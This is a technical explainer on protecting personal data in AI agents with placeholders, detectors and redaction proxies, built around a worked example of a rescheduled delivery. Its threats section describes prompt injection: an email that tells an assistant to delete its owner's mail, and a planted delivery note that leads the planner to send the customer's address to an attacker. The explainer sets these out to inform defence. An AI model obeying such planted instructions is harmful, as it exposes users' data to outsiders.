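# Pseudonymisation and placeholder substitution for personal data in AI agents

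## Planner, executor and placeholder: the basic design

Pseudonymisation lets an AI agent work with personal data without exposing that data to its language model. Before text reaches the model, trusted software replaces each name, address or account number with a placeholder such as EMAIL_1. The model plans with the placeholders. When a planned action, such as sending a message, needs a real value, the trusted software puts the value back and carries out the action.

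The language model is the planner. It reads the task and chooses which tools to call and with which arguments. The executor is the trusted software that carries out those calls and is allowed to see real values. A mapping table, which the planner cannot access, links each placeholder to the value it hides. Resolving a placeholder means replacing it with that value.

### How a value reaches the model and stays there

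A language model on its own only produces text. An agent runs the model in a loop. *Agents That Know Too Much* (Lahjouji and Colaco, 2026), a survey of agent privacy, describes this loop as reasoning about a goal, choosing an action, observing the outcome and repeating until the task is done. The actions are mostly tool calls. A tool is a function that a developer offers to the model, such as a database query, and a tool call is structured output that names the function and supplies its arguments. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers building on its Claude models, the model never runs anything itself. For the most common kind of tool, the developer's application extracts the arguments, runs the operation and sends the output back in its next request.

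The privacy problem starts with that next request. The interface to Claude is stateless, as Anthropic's *API usage primer for Claude* explains, so the application sends the full conversation every time. The planner's context (the text it reads before producing its next step) contains the user's message, every call so far and whatever each tool returned, so it grows with each call. A customer record that arrives in the second request is normally sent again in every later one.

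Tools also return data that nobody requested. *SlotGuard* (Xia and Park, 2026) describes a debugging command that listed the programs running on a machine, including a line that contained a secret access key. No user had typed the key into the conversation, but once the listing was in the transcript, the key stayed there across later turns.

Data in the model's context gets copied elsewhere, most obviously into the provider's logs. According to OpenAI's *Your data*, OpenAI keeps abuse-monitoring logs, which may include prompts and responses, for up to 30 days by default, and keeps conversation threads until the customer deletes them. According to Anthropic's *API and data retention*, Anthropic does not retain conversation content by default for most of its models, but it keeps transcripts of the agent sessions it hosts until the customer deletes them, and content that its safety systems flag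 for up to two years.

The user's own disk can also hold copies. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, writes anything that passes through a tool to a plaintext transcript there, which is deleted after 30 days by default. If the user submits a transcript through the feedback command, Anthropic keeps a copy for five years, according to its *Data usage*.

The clean-up does not delete the agent's memory files, the notes it carries from one session to the next. Lahjouji and Colaco warn that data an agent writes to memory in one session can be shown to a different user in another. *Disclosure Begets Disclosure* (2026) found that, in conversations with simulated users, consulting memory improved an agent's answers but also let an observer infer more about the user, by a margin that grew with the number of sessions.

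Finally, the planner can copy any value in its context into any later tool call, such as a support ticket, a search query or a request to another company's service. Data sent to a third-party tool server falls under that party's retention policy, as OpenAI points out to its customers.

### One delivery, traced twice

Maria Keller has ordered a cello from an online shop, for delivery on Tuesday to 14 Linden Street, Leeds. She writes to the shop's support agent, gives her name and email address, maria.keller@example.org, and asks for delivery on Thursday instead, because she teaches on Tuesdays. The agent has three tools. `find_order` looks up an order by email address, `move_delivery` books a new day with the courier, and `send_email` sends a confirmation.

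With raw data, the planner reads her message and writes `find_order(email="maria.keller@example.org")`. The executor runs the query and returns the order record, which contains her name, email address and street address. The planner copies the street address into a `move_delivery` call, and the courier's system confirms a Thursday delivery from its Leeds South depot. Then the planner writes the confirmation email.

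The task takes four requests to the model provider, one with the message alone and one after each tool result. Maria's email address appears in her message, in the look-up, in the record and in the "to" field of the confirmation. Each request repeats what came before, so the provider receives the address eleven times in total.

With placeholders, the same job runs like this:

| Step | What the planner reads or writes | What the executor does |
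|---|---|---|
| Message arrives | NAME_1 (EMAIL_1) wants Tuesday's delivery on Thursday, because she teaches on Tuesdays | Replaces the name and email address and enters both in the mapping table |
| Look-up | `find_order(email="EMAIL_1")` | Resolves EMAIL_1 and queries the order database |
| Record comes back | Order 58213, one cello, NAME_1, EMAIL_1, ADDRESS_1, Tuesday | Reuses the two existing placeholders and adds ADDRESS_1 for the street address |
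| Rebooking | `move_delivery(order="58213", address="ADDRESS_1", day="Thursday")` | Resolves ADDRESS_1 and books with the courier |
| Courier confirms | Thursday, from the Leeds South depot | Finds nothing on its list to replace |
| Confirmation | `send_email(to="EMAIL_1", body="Dear NAME_1, your cello will arrive on Thursday.")` | Resolves both placeholders and sends the email |

Maria gets the same email with or without the substitution, and the provider now holds eleven copies of the string EMAIL_1. The substitution doesn't affect the result here because no step depends on the actual address. The planner only has to identify ADDRESS_1 as an address that the courier needs. Typed placeholders like this one indicate the kind of value they hide. With opaque placeholders, such as MASK_1 and MASK_2, the planner would have to infer the kind of value from the surrounding text. A system can also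 use surrogates, which are realistic false values such as an invented name.

Where the swap takes place determines how many of the other copies become harmless. Xia and Park put theirs mainly inside the program that runs the agent's loop, so it replaces personal data before a tool's output joins the transcript. A swap on the network connection to the provider would remove the raw values from the provider's copy but leave them in the agent's own files.

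### Redaction, pseudonymisation, anonymisation, tokenisation

The provider in the second trace still learns that a customer of this shop teaches on Tuesdays, has bought a cello and lives within reach of a depot in Leeds. A colleague of Maria's might be able to identify her from that. Such details are called quasi-identifiers because each fits many people and they identify someone only in combination. A direct identifier, such as a passport number or a full name with an address, identifies a person by itself. *ToolMinimize* (2026), a design for software that trims the arguments of tool calls, lists email addresses, phone numbers and US social security numbers as direct identifiers, and age, postcode, occupation and date of birth as quasi-identifiers. The basic placeholder design removes direct identifiers but leaves most other details. Re-identification is working out who a text is about from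 the details that remain.

Writers often mix up the terms for what a system does to a value. Redaction removes the value permanently. If the shop had redacted Maria's record, nobody could have used it to send her the confirmation. Pseudonymisation replaces the identifier with a stand-in and keeps the means of reversal elsewhere (data protection law defines the term more strictly). *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs* (2026) applies it to documents that lawyers and clinicians paste into chatbots. The chatbot receives the document with placeholders, while the mapping stays on the user's machine, where software restores the original values in the answer.

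Anonymisation is stricter than pseudonymisation because nobody should have a realistic way to trace the data back to the person. This rules out a mapping table and requires treating the quasi-identifiers too. An agent that has to deliver a cello to Maria Keller cannot work on anonymous data, because some part of the system must be able to find her. Xia and Park do not promise full anonymisation for their system, since the format of a hidden value and the text around it can still reveal information.

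Tokenisation is the payment industry's word for replacing a value with a stand-in, and some writers on agents use it too. In language modelling, it instead means splitting text into the small units that a model processes.

### Three threats

How much placeholders help depends on whom the shop is worried about. One possibility is the model provider. Lahjouji and Colaco use the standard term "honest but curious" for a party that follows the protocol but tries to learn more than it should. Xia and Park design against roughly this kind of provider, one that runs the model correctly but may keep what it receives.

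A provider can retain and study prompts without acting in bad faith. Since 9 June 2026 Anthropic has kept prompts and outputs of its Mythos-class models for 30 days, even for customers who had arranged for zero retention. According to Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models*, the company does this because some attacks only become visible when it analyses many requests together. By default its staff cannot read the retained conversations, and a small group of approved reviewers gets access only through a controlled and logged path. Stored text can still leak by accident. Xia and Park recall a fault in ChatGPT that showed some users the titles of other people's chats. Placeholders work well against this threat because anyone who reads the log finds EMAIL_1 instead of the address, though the details about the cello and the Tuesday teaching are still there.

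The planner may also disclose or misuse data when no attacker is involved. *ToolPrivacyBench* (Hu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) ran nine agents through synthetic business workflows and checked which private facts reached which tools. The agents scored between 92 and 98 out of 100 for task success, but they also passed on facts that the receiving tool did not need. Disclosure was most frequent in tickets, at about 51% of the cases where a fact did not belong there, followed by handoffs to other teams at about 35%.

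*AgentCIScope* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 agents on 936 tasks across email, documents, calendars and other applications. The share of tasks with a leak ranged from 32.5% for Claude Opus 5 running in Claude Code to 94.4% for Gemini 3.8 Flash in Google's agent framework. These figures probably overstate everyday leakage because the researchers worded the tasks to encourage oversharing, for example by asking for a more self-contained briefing, though they never requested the protected facts.

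Agents leaked credit-card information in 17.1% of cases and social security numbers in 29.4%, against 76.5% for booking details and 84.7% for personal preferences. This pattern is awkward for placeholder designs because card and social security numbers are easy to replace, while a preference, or a remark about teaching on Tuesdays, usually stays in the text.

A placeholder also does not stop the planner from sending a value to the wrong place. If the planner adds ADDRESS_1 to a ticket that outside contractors read, an executor that resolves every placeholder will write 14 Linden Street into the ticket. *ArguShield* (2026) singles out this failure, in which a tool call can have the right format and complete the task while releasing values that the receiver does not need. The placeholder does limit the damage in one respect, because the planner cannot repeat to another customer an address it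 has never received.

The remaining threat is that the planner may follow instructions hidden in the data. Language models read instructions and content as one stream of text, so an outsider who can plant a sentence in the content may be able to steer the model. This attack is called prompt injection. The software developer Simon Willison's usual example is an email that tells an assistant to delete all of its owner's emails, which the assistant might do even if it was only asked to summarise the inbox. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) also describes planted instructions that make an assistant send out private data.

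In Maria's case, the planted sentence could be in her order's delivery notes and ask for the customer's details to be sent to an outside email address. Replacing her name and street with placeholders leaves that sentence intact. If the planner follows it, the planner writes a `send_email` call with ADDRESS_1 in the body, and an executor that doesn't check the recipient replaces the placeholder with her real address and sends it to the attacker. Placeholders help here only if the executor does not restore the value for that recipient, or if the planner never reads the delivery notes.

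### Where the idea came from

Replacing sensitive data with placeholders is older than language models. In the 2000s, payment processors began to offer tokenisation to shops that stored card numbers to charge returning customers, because those numbers were worth stealing. The processor keeps the card number in a protected vault and gives the shop a token, which the shop sends back to charge the card. A thief who copies the shop's database gets tokens that are of little use anywhere else. Like the shop, the planner in an agent can order the use of a value that it does not hold.

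Willison applied a similar separation to agents in April 2023, as a defence against prompt injection. In his proposal, a privileged language model takes the user's request and has access to tools, while a quarantined language model reads untrusted content and has no tools. A controller, written as ordinary software, passes data between them.

If the user wants a summary of the latest email, the privileged model issues a command to fetch it, and the controller does so and stores the text as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then issues a command to summarise `$VAR1`. The controller passes the real text to the quarantined model and stores the result as `$VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model issues a command to display `$VAR2`. It has received the two variable names but not the email or the summary, so an instruction hidden in either text cannot reach it. In the terms used above, the privileged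 model is a planner and the controller is an executor.

The quarantined model reads everything, so the scheme keeps data secret from the provider only if that model runs somewhere the user trusts. Such secrecy was not the scheme's aim. Willison called his solution "pretty bad". It makes software more complex and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model defeats the whole scheme. An attacker can also still persuade users to copy their own data out. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, builds on Willison's proposal and fixes a flaw in it.

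Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, published on 4 November 2025, describes a version of this design meant for privacy. It concerns agents that write short programs to operate their tools through the Model Context Protocol, an open standard for connecting agents to tools. In its example, an agent copies customers' contact details from a spreadsheet into Salesforce, a sales database. The client software intercepts the rows and replaces names, email addresses and phone numbers with placeholders before the model sees them, then looks up the real values when the next tool call needs them. The personal data therefore reaches Salesforce without passing through the model. Willison (2025) thought the proposal sensible but noted that Anthropic had released no code for it.

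## Finding the personal data before the planner reads it

In Maria Keller's delivery, the order record came from a database with an `email` column, so the executor could replace the value in that column without inspecting it. Her message was free text, where any word might be part of a name, so the executor had to inspect the text to find what to replace.

Field labels are the more reliable guide. A developer decides once which columns hold personal data, and the rule then covers new names in any spelling or alphabet. The rule fails when people put data in the wrong field, such as a phone number in the field for a company name, and it doesn't help with a notes column. If Maria's delivery notes read "leave it with Mrs Okafor at number 12", no label marks the neighbour's name. Emails, web pages and log files often have no labels.

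For free text, the executor needs a detector, which is software that returns the position and type of each personal value. The detector has to run on a machine the user trusts. *CAPED* (2026), a design for agents that operate phones, rules out asking a cloud model what to hide, because the task and the screen may already contain the private data. Avoiding the cloud favours small, fast detectors.

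### Patterns, models and known names

The simplest detector is a pattern, usually a regular expression, that describes the shape of a string. An email address, for example, is a run of characters followed by an @ sign and a domain name. Patterns can also include neighbouring words. In *Redacting Personal Data*, Yashwant, Sharma and colleagues (2026) replace a date only if it follows "DOB" or "Date of birth", so the years of employment in a CV stay readable.

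Many official numbers contain a check digit, which lets the detector reject lookalikes. For a bank card, the detector counts from the right, doubles every second digit, subtracts nine from any result above nine and adds everything up. The total for a valid card is a multiple of ten, so about nine in ten random numbers of the same length fail. A real card number with one mistyped digit also fails, so a detector that requires a valid checksum misses it and lets the remaining correct digits reach the planner.

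Names have no fixed format, so named-entity recognition finds them with a model trained on annotated text to identify words that refer to people, places or organisations. spaCy, an open-source library for language processing, includes such models. Presidio, an open-source framework that Microsoft originally developed, combines them with patterns, checksums and context words.

Privacy Filter, a detector that OpenAI released in April 2026, covers eight categories: people, addresses, email addresses, phone numbers, web addresses, dates, account numbers and secrets such as passwords. According to its model card (OpenAI (2026)), it first estimates whether each token (a word or part of a word) begins, continues or ends a value in one of these categories, is a complete value by itself, or is ordinary text. A decoding step then picks the most plausible coherent sequence of labels, so that "14 Linden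 Street" is labelled as one address rather than three fragments. The model is small enough to run on a laptop.

Such a model depends heavily on context. In OpenAI's tests on short synthetic English examples, Privacy Filter found 92% of phone numbers when a phrase like "my home landline number" came before the number, 57% when it came after, and 32% when the number stood alone. Field labels can also help here, because an executor can provide context by passing the column name along with the value.

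A small language model can also rate how sensitive a passage is. In *MemPrivacy*, Chen, Zhao and colleagues (2026) trained models with 0.6 to 4 billion parameters to list every private passage in a message, with its type and one of four sensitivity levels. The lowest level covers ordinary preferences, which stay visible. The second covers details that identify a person, the third covers details whose exposure could cause serious harm, such as medical records, and the fourth covers passwords and other credentials that a thief could use immediately. Users choose the level at which hiding starts.

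For free text, the method that takes the least computation is to search for the names of people already in the system's records. Once the shop has loaded Maria's record, the executor can look for "Maria Keller", "Keller" and "Maria" in everything else it reads. Yashwant and colleagues call this the known-entity rule. Their version ignores case and looks for the longest form first. It would find "MARIA" at the bottom of an email, but it would miss Mrs Okafor, whose name isn't in the record. If a customer were called June, it would also hide the month.

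### When two detectors find the same text

Most systems run several detectors, and their findings overlap. In maria.keller@example.org, for example, the email pattern matches the whole string, while the known-entity rule matches "maria" and "keller". Yashwant and colleagues sort all findings by starting position, with the longer one first if two start together, and skip any finding that overlaps one already accepted. In this example, that keeps the email address and discards the two names inside it.

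This rule can expose personal data when an earlier finding is wrong. Suppose a model takes "Maria Keller 14" for a name because the street address follows on the next line. The address "14 Linden Street" overlaps that finding and starts later, so the software skips the address and leaves "Linden Street" visible. Yashwant and colleagues found that spaCy extended names across line breaks, and they now cut every name at the end of its line. Merging overlapping findings into one long span would be safer, but the planner would get one placeholder for both the name and the address.

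They compared four combinations on 100 synthetic CVs containing 900 personal values. All four used the known-entity rule, with the CV's owner as the known person.

| Design | Values caught | Median time per CV | Start-up time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Patterns only | 88.9% | 0.20 ms | 0.8 ms |
| Presidio, with extra patterns for addresses and birth dates | 100% | 37.59 ms | 5,021 ms |
| Presidio for names, patterns for the rest | 100% | 30.23 ms | 1,417 ms |
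| spaCy for names, patterns for the rest | 100% | 13.48 ms | 1,699 ms |

Speed hardly matters, because the median call to the language model took 9,120 ms and even Presidio added only 0.41%. Each CV named one referee whom the system did not know. Patterns alone missed all 100 of these referees, and the designs with a model found every one. These accuracy figures are weaker evidence, because the generated CVs were short, shared one layout and took those referees from a list of only five names. Yashwant and colleagues expect every design to miss some values in real text.

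### Why long documents leak

A detector's recall is the share of personal values that it finds. Call it *r*, and suppose that the detector finds or misses each value independently of the others. The probability that it finds all *n* values in a document is then *r* multiplied by itself *n* times, and the probability of at least one miss is

1 − *r*ⁿ

At 98% recall, a message with two values, like Maria's, leaks at least one of them about 4% of the time. A contract with 30 values does so about 45% of the time. To keep the contract's risk down to 2%, *r*³⁰ must be at least 0.98, which requires a recall of about 99.93%, or one miss in roughly 1,500 values.

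A recall of 98% is a good result. OpenAI reports that Privacy Filter reaches 98.1% on a corrected version of a widely used benchmark. That figure counts tokens, so the share of values it finds in full may be lower. For an agent, the number of values, *n*, also grows with every tool result that contains new ones.

Real misses are not independent. In the CV test, patterns alone had a recall of 88.9%. With nine values per CV, the formula predicts a leak in about 65% of CVs, but all of them leaked because each contained exactly one name of a kind that patterns cannot find. When misses are concentrated in a few badly typed documents, fewer documents leak than the formula predicts.

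In *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs*, Vladimir Beskorovainyi tested detectors on whole synthetic documents, 1,000 in Russian and 1,000 in UK English. They included contracts, business letters and hospital discharge summaries, and held an average of about 30 relevant values each in Russian and about 26 in UK English. He ran five existing open tools, a set of patterns and his own engine, and counted the documents in which at least one whole value stayed visible.

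| Detector | Russian documents with a leak | UK documents with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| pii-guard (Russian only) | 60.8% | – |
| GLiNER Guard Omni | 99.6% | 58.3% |
| Presidio | 87.1% | 61.1% |
| OpenAI Privacy Filter | 97.0% | 81.1% |
| Prompt Anonymizer (English only) | – | 100% |
| Patterns only | 100% | 100% |
| Beskorovainyi's engine | 0.3% | 0.2% |

The formula is fairly accurate here. GLiNER Guard, the best existing tool for UK English, fully covered 95.4% of the identification numbers and 88.9% of the names, addresses and organisations. For 26 values, the formula gives about 88% of documents containing something not fully hidden, and Beskorovainyi counted 83.5%. The 58.3% in the table is lower because it doesn't count addresses and organisations that the tool only partly hid.

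Some of the leaks come from how the test was built. About 40% of the documents contained deliberate noise, such as typos or numbers written out in words. Without the noisy documents, the best existing tools leaked in 41% of Russian and 38% of UK documents. pii-guard doesn't look for organisations, and excluding them lowers its leak rate from 60.8% to 31.5%. Other misses would be just as likely in ordinary letters. For example, GLiNER Guard sometimes hid a person's full name in the text but missed it in the signature.

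Beskorovainyi's engine addresses that last problem. It combines pii-guard and GLiNER Guard with checksum rules and adds no new model. Once it finds one mention of a value, it hides all the others, including Russian surnames in other grammatical cases, so a value leaks only if the detectors miss every mention of it.

The engine's figures of 0.3% and 0.2% probably overstate its accuracy, because Beskorovainyi developed it on six earlier sets of documents from the same generator. He published the final set and the rules for judging it before the run, so he could not have tuned the engine to those documents, but he could have tuned it to the generator's style. The engine and the generator also share checksum code. The gap was much smaller on UK texts from an NVIDIA dataset, where the engine had leaks in 0.9% of texts and GLiNER Guard in 4.0%. Most of the identification numbers in those texts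 also came from Beskorovainyi's generator. Of the 553 that NVIDIA had supplied, the engine found 552 and GLiNER Guard 548. Nobody has tested the engine on real documents.

### One detector, two very different scores

A detector's score also depends on what the test counts as private. Chen and colleagues tested Privacy Filter on two sets of conversations and reported its F1 score, which combines recall with precision (the share of findings that are correct). It scored 85.3 out of 100 on a set drawn from PersonaMem-v2, a benchmark for personalised assistants, but only 35.5 on their own MemPrivacy-Bench. Their best model scored 94.5 and 86.0 on the same two sets, respectively.

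Chen and colleagues attribute the low score partly to Privacy Filter's use of eight broad categories and partly to its weaker performance on Chinese, the language of half of MemPrivacy-Bench. Their counts of private passages support the first explanation. In PersonaMem-v2, three-quarters of these passages are identifying details such as names and contact data, which Privacy Filter was built to find. In MemPrivacy-Bench, nearly two-thirds belong to the two most sensitive levels. Those levels include medical histories, and Privacy Filter has no category for illness.

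About 81% of the messages in MemPrivacy-Bench contain something private, compared with 22% in the PersonaMem-v2 set, which Chen and colleagues consider closer to real use. A finding gets full marks only if its text, type and sensitivity level are all correct, so a detector can hide a passage and still lose points for labelling it wrongly. Privacy Filter's score of 35.5 therefore does not mean that it left two-thirds of the private text visible.

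The MemPrivacy models had an advantage on MemPrivacy-Bench because they were trained on conversations from the same source. On PersonaMem-v2, which they had not been trained on, the best one scored only about two points higher than DeepSeek-V3.2-Think, a far larger general model. However, the MemPrivacy model took 0.44 seconds per message, compared with 39.6 for DeepSeek. Chen and colleagues timed the MemPrivacy models on a data-centre GPU, so the models would be slower on a phone.

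### Screenshots

Some agents operate a computer by receiving screenshots and responding with clicks and keystrokes. To hide Maria's address from such an agent, the trusted software has to read the characters in the image, recognise them as an address and cover the right pixels. An error at any of these steps can expose the address.

The first step, text recognition, already loses a good deal of personal data. *LeakageBench* (Vijaya Kumar, Venkatesh and Yamshchikov, 2026) tested systems on 500 pages of business documents, many of them scans. Two standard text-recognition programs failed to recover 14.6% and 17.9% of the names, contact details and reference numbers, and a text-based detector is unlikely to catch a garbled value. Even the best complete systems left at least one such value unprotected on 96.8% of pages. That figure overstates the exposure, because the test accepted a covering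 box only if it closely matched the annotated area and had the right type, so a name hidden by a badly drawn box could still count as unprotected.

Web pages are usually sharper than scans, but a screenshot can capture data that is only partly typed. If an agent takes one while Maria is entering her email address, the form may show "maria.kel", which no email pattern recognises. *WebPII* (Zhao, 2026) therefore includes thousands of half-completed forms in its set of 44,865 synthetic images of shopping sites. A detector trained on these images scored 0.753 on a scale from 0 to 1 for locating sensitive regions and took 20 milliseconds, while text recognition followed by Presidio scored 0.183 and took 1.3 seconds. Part of the gap in scores is probably due to the benchmark's definition of sensitive data, which includes product and order details that Presidio was not designed to find.

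Large vision models often recognise that a screenshot contains private data but fail to locate it. *GUIGuard-Bench* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested eight models on screenshots from real agent sessions. On average, the models judged correctly whether a screenshot contained private content in 89.0% of cases on Android and 63.3% on PCs, but they located only 52.9% of the private elements on Android and 13.5% on PCs. Wang and colleagues attribute the lower PC scores to desktop screens having more text and often showing several private items close together.

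### The cost of hiding too much

A detector that hid everything would have perfect recall but leave the planner nothing to work with. Real detectors also hide too much, though to a lesser degree. Yashwant and colleagues found that spaCy labelled the "jack" in "pallet jack", a warehouse tool, as a person, and they had to add a list of words the software must never treat as names. In Beskorovainyi's UK documents, about one in five of the fragments that Presidio hid contained no personal data.

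OpenAI's announcement of Privacy Filter shows a sample email that gives a product's launch date. In the output, the filter has replaced that date with a placeholder for a private date. An agent planning the launch from the filtered email would not know the launch date.

Such mistakes do less harm when the executor can restore the value. If the shop's detector hid the word "Thursday" in Maria's message, the planner could still pass the placeholder to the courier. But it could not check whether that Thursday was a public holiday or whether the courier delivered on Thursdays.

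Developers can set Privacy Filter to hide longer stretches of text or fewer of them, and further training quickly adapts it to a different policy. In one of OpenAI's tests, which used legal and medical questions, only the details of the person asking counted as private. Privacy Filter also hid other people's details at first, and only 41% of the tokens it marked were correct. After further training on a tenth of the available examples, that share rose to 96%.

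A fixed policy cannot anticipate every task. The name of a contact on a phone screen is private when the agent is checking the weather, but the agent needs it when the user wants to send that person a photo. *CAPED* therefore decides what information the cloud model receives for each task and screen. In *MaskClaw* (Zhao, Zheng and colleagues, 2026), the local software asks the user in doubtful cases and turns the user's corrections into rules for later screens.

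## Redaction proxies: swapping values out and back

Once a detector has marked the personal data, other software has to replace it and later put it back. For this, many developers use a redaction proxy, a program that relays all traffic between the agent and the model provider. The agent sends its requests to the proxy's address instead of the provider's, so the developer hardly has to change the agent.

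A proxy splits the executor's work. The proxy keeps the mapping table and resolves placeholders, while the agent's own software runs the tools and handles real values throughout. In Maria Keller's delivery, each piece of text has one version on each side of the proxy:

| What passes through | Agent's side | Provider's side |
|---|---|---|
| Maria's message, going out | Maria Keller (maria.keller@example.org) wants Tuesday's delivery on Thursday | NAME_1 (EMAIL_1) wants Tuesday's delivery on Thursday |
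| Look-up, coming back | `find_order(email="maria.keller@example.org")` | `find_order(email="EMAIL_1")` |
| Order record, going out | Order 58213, Maria Keller, maria.keller@example.org, 14 Linden Street, Leeds | Order 58213, NAME_1, EMAIL_1, ADDRESS_1 |
| Rebooking, coming back | `move_delivery(order="58213", address="14 Linden Street, Leeds", day="Thursday")` | `move_delivery(order="58213", address="ADDRESS_1", day="Thursday")` |
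| Final reply, coming back | Your cello will arrive on Thursday. I have sent a confirmation to maria.keller@example.org. | Your cello will arrive on Thursday. I have sent a confirmation to EMAIL_1. |

The agent's copy of the conversation contains the real values, even in tool calls that the planner wrote with placeholders, so the proxy has to redact the whole conversation again each time the agent resends it. In the fourth request, the proxy has to replace Maria's email address in four places, always with the same placeholder.

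### When tool results skip the swap

If the proxy rewrote only what Maria types, the provider would receive her full order record, including her name, email address and street address, in the second, third and fourth requests. The planner would also copy 14 Linden Street into its `move_delivery` call. The placeholder in Maria's message would no longer hide her email address, because the provider could see that a search for EMAIL_1 returned the record of maria.keller@example.org.

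LangChain's *PIIMiddleware*, a component of a Python library for building agents, has this gap by default. It checks user messages but not tool results, though developers can change both settings. By default it also replaces values permanently, so Maria's agent would search the database for the text [REDACTED_EMAIL] and find no order.

Strathweb's *PII guardrails for .NET applications* describes tool results as the most underappreciated route for personal data into an agent. In its demonstration, a support agent's look-up tool returns a customer's email address, phone number and social security number. When the check on tool results is on, labels replace all three values before the model reads them. This version doesn't restore the original values, so the employee who asked for the customer's contact details also gets labels.

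### Where to put the swap

A developer can build the swap into a network proxy, the agent itself, or the software that connects the agent to its tools.

| Position | What it can see | What it cannot see or protect |
|---|---|---|
| Model gateway | Finished requests and answers, from every agent that connects through it | The reason for a tool call; real values in the agent's own files and logs |
| Agent software | Messages, tool calls and tool results as separate items | Traffic from other agents |
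| Tool server | Its own data, with field labels | The user's message and the other tools |
| Tool client | Data going to and from all connected tools | What the user types into the chat |

Gateways are popular because one installation covers many programs. Help Net Security's *Open-source privacy proxy masks PII before prompts reach external AI services* describes a gateway from the software company Dataiku that runs on the user's machine and replaces personal data with surrogates. A browser extension lets people use it when they type into ChatGPT. LiteLLM, a gateway for sending requests to various models, has separate settings for masking the request and restoring the original values in the answer, so a developer who enables only the first gets answers that still contain placeholders.

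However, a gateway works on finished requests. Xia and Park point out that it does not normally have access to local files or to what the agent is trying to do, so it cannot easily check whether a value belongs in the call. Because traffic to the provider is encrypted, the user's computer may also have to trust a new certificate that lets the proxy read that traffic. Xia and Park recommend a gateway as a last line of defence.

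The swap can happen earlier, inside the agent. Yashwant and colleagues put theirs between the code that assembles the prompt and the code that sends it, so the application's logs and traces contain the same placeholders as the provider's copy. By contrast, LangChain's now-deprecated JavaScript component, *piiRedactionMiddleware*, replaces and restores values, including those in tool results, but writes the restored values back into the agent's state so that the tools can use them. LangChain warns that personal data may remain in saved checkpoints, logs and traces.

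A tool server has the best information about its own data, such as which column holds email addresses. But if each server kept its own mapping table, the courier's server could not resolve an ADDRESS_1 that the order database had created. The design that Anthropic described in 2025 avoids this problem by swapping values in the client, the part of the agent's software that talks to all the tool servers.

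In Anthropic's example of copying contact details from a spreadsheet to Salesforce, the model's program prints only the number of records it has updated. The rows stay in the environment that runs the program, so placeholders are a second layer of protection. If the program also prints the rows, perhaps so the model can check them, the client's placeholders hide the values.

Developers can use the same mechanism to set fixed rules about which tools may receive which data. The mechanism requires a secure environment for running model-written code, with resource limits and monitoring. A client that handles only tool traffic would also leave Maria's opening message unprotected, so the shop would need a second swap for the chat.

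### Pookie, a gateway in detail

The French cloud company OVHcloud uses a gateway called Pookie to protect its engineers' data when they work with coding agents. According to OVHcloud's *Protect sensitive data from AI agents with a redaction proxy*, Pookie's developer had first cleaned log files with a find-and-replace script, which was easy to forget to run by hand. The script also replaced every private network address with the same label, so the model could not tell two servers apart, and the developer had to put the real values back into each answer.

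A Pookie placeholder looks like `__PK_PRIVIP_fe44bc609bf6__`. The middle part identifies the hidden value to the model as a private IP address. OVHcloud's *Redact secrets from LLM prompts* explains that Pookie computes the last part with an HMAC, a function that turns a value and a secret key into a fixed-length fingerprint. The same value and key always give the same fingerprint, so Pookie can replace an address consistently throughout a conversation without looking anything up.

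Nobody can reverse the fingerprint to get the value, so Pookie has to store the value to swap it back in later. Strathweb's reversible version needs no store, because its placeholder is the encrypted value. But the provider then holds Maria's email address in encrypted form, and anyone who obtains the key can read it in old logs. A thief with only Pookie's key would have to guess the value, which is still feasible for phone numbers because a computer can calculate the fingerprint of every possible number and look for a match.

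Pookie encrypts the stored values and, by default, deletes them 72 hours after it last wrote the entry. OVHcloud chose this period so that an engineer can stop on Friday and continue on Monday.

Pookie keeps each user's values in a separate namespace, a section of the store that it derives from that user's own credential with the model provider. If the cello shop and a bookshop shared a proxy without namespaces, a malicious provider could take the placeholder for Maria's email address from the cello shop's requests and write it into an answer to the bookshop. The proxy would then replace the placeholder with maria.keller@example.org. With namespaces, Pookie searches only the bookshop's section and finds nothing. An attacker who can write to the database cannot get around this by copying Maria's entry into the bookshop's section, because each encrypted entry is tied to its original place and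 fails a check anywhere else.

Even with namespaces, a user's own agent can send a restored value to the wrong recipient. OVHcloud lists this among Pookie's limits, and preventing it requires checks on each tool call.

Answers usually arrive in small pieces while the model is still writing, and a placeholder can begin in one piece and end in the next. Pookie holds back just enough text to avoid restoring half a placeholder. Attic Security's *Why LLMs Hate Fake Data* describes a similar proxy, which the company uses to analyse security alerts with Claude. That proxy always holds back the last 80 characters. Tool call arguments are in JSON, which encloses text in quotation marks. If a password contained a quotation mark, inserting it unchanged would end the text early and break the call, so Pookie marks such characters as part of the value.

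Pookie blocks an outgoing request if it cannot read all of it or cannot reach its store, because nobody can take back a secret that has reached the provider. If it cannot restore a placeholder in the answer, it lets the placeholder through and raises an alert, since the answer only goes to the user's own machine. Pookie has no off switch, so when a provider introduces a new message format, agents may stop working until the developer adds support for it.

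OVHcloud's *Spec-driven development with AI agents* recounts how the alerts revealed that a model was inventing placeholders. The model had seen folder names full of placeholders, copied their pattern, and tried to open folders that did not exist. Nothing leaked, but an invented placeholder looked exactly like a real one whose value had gone missing from the store. Pookie now writes a second record for each placeholder, which contains no secret and shows only that Pookie created the placeholder and when. These records last 12 days, four times as long as the values, so the operator can tell an expired placeholder from an invented one during that time.

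Pookie would do less for Maria than the table at the start of this section suggests. It finds values with patterns and a test for random-looking strings, so it would hide her email address but leave her name and 14 Linden Street. When its developer tried adding named-entity recognition, processing time per request rose from about 200 milliseconds to 30 seconds. Name recognition was much faster on the short CVs that Yashwant and colleagues used, but a coding agent's request can include a long conversation and whole files.

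### How placeholders get lost

A proxy restores a placeholder by finding it in the planner's text, so it can miss one that the planner has changed. Attic Security's first version replaced email addresses with tags such as [User_Email_1]. Claude was supposed to use these tags in database queries, but it instead made up a realistic user called sarah.kowalski and searched for her. The company then switched to surrogate email addresses, but Claude wrote queries with only the username, the part before the @ sign. The proxy did not recognise it, so the queries found nothing. The proxy now registers both the full address and the username.

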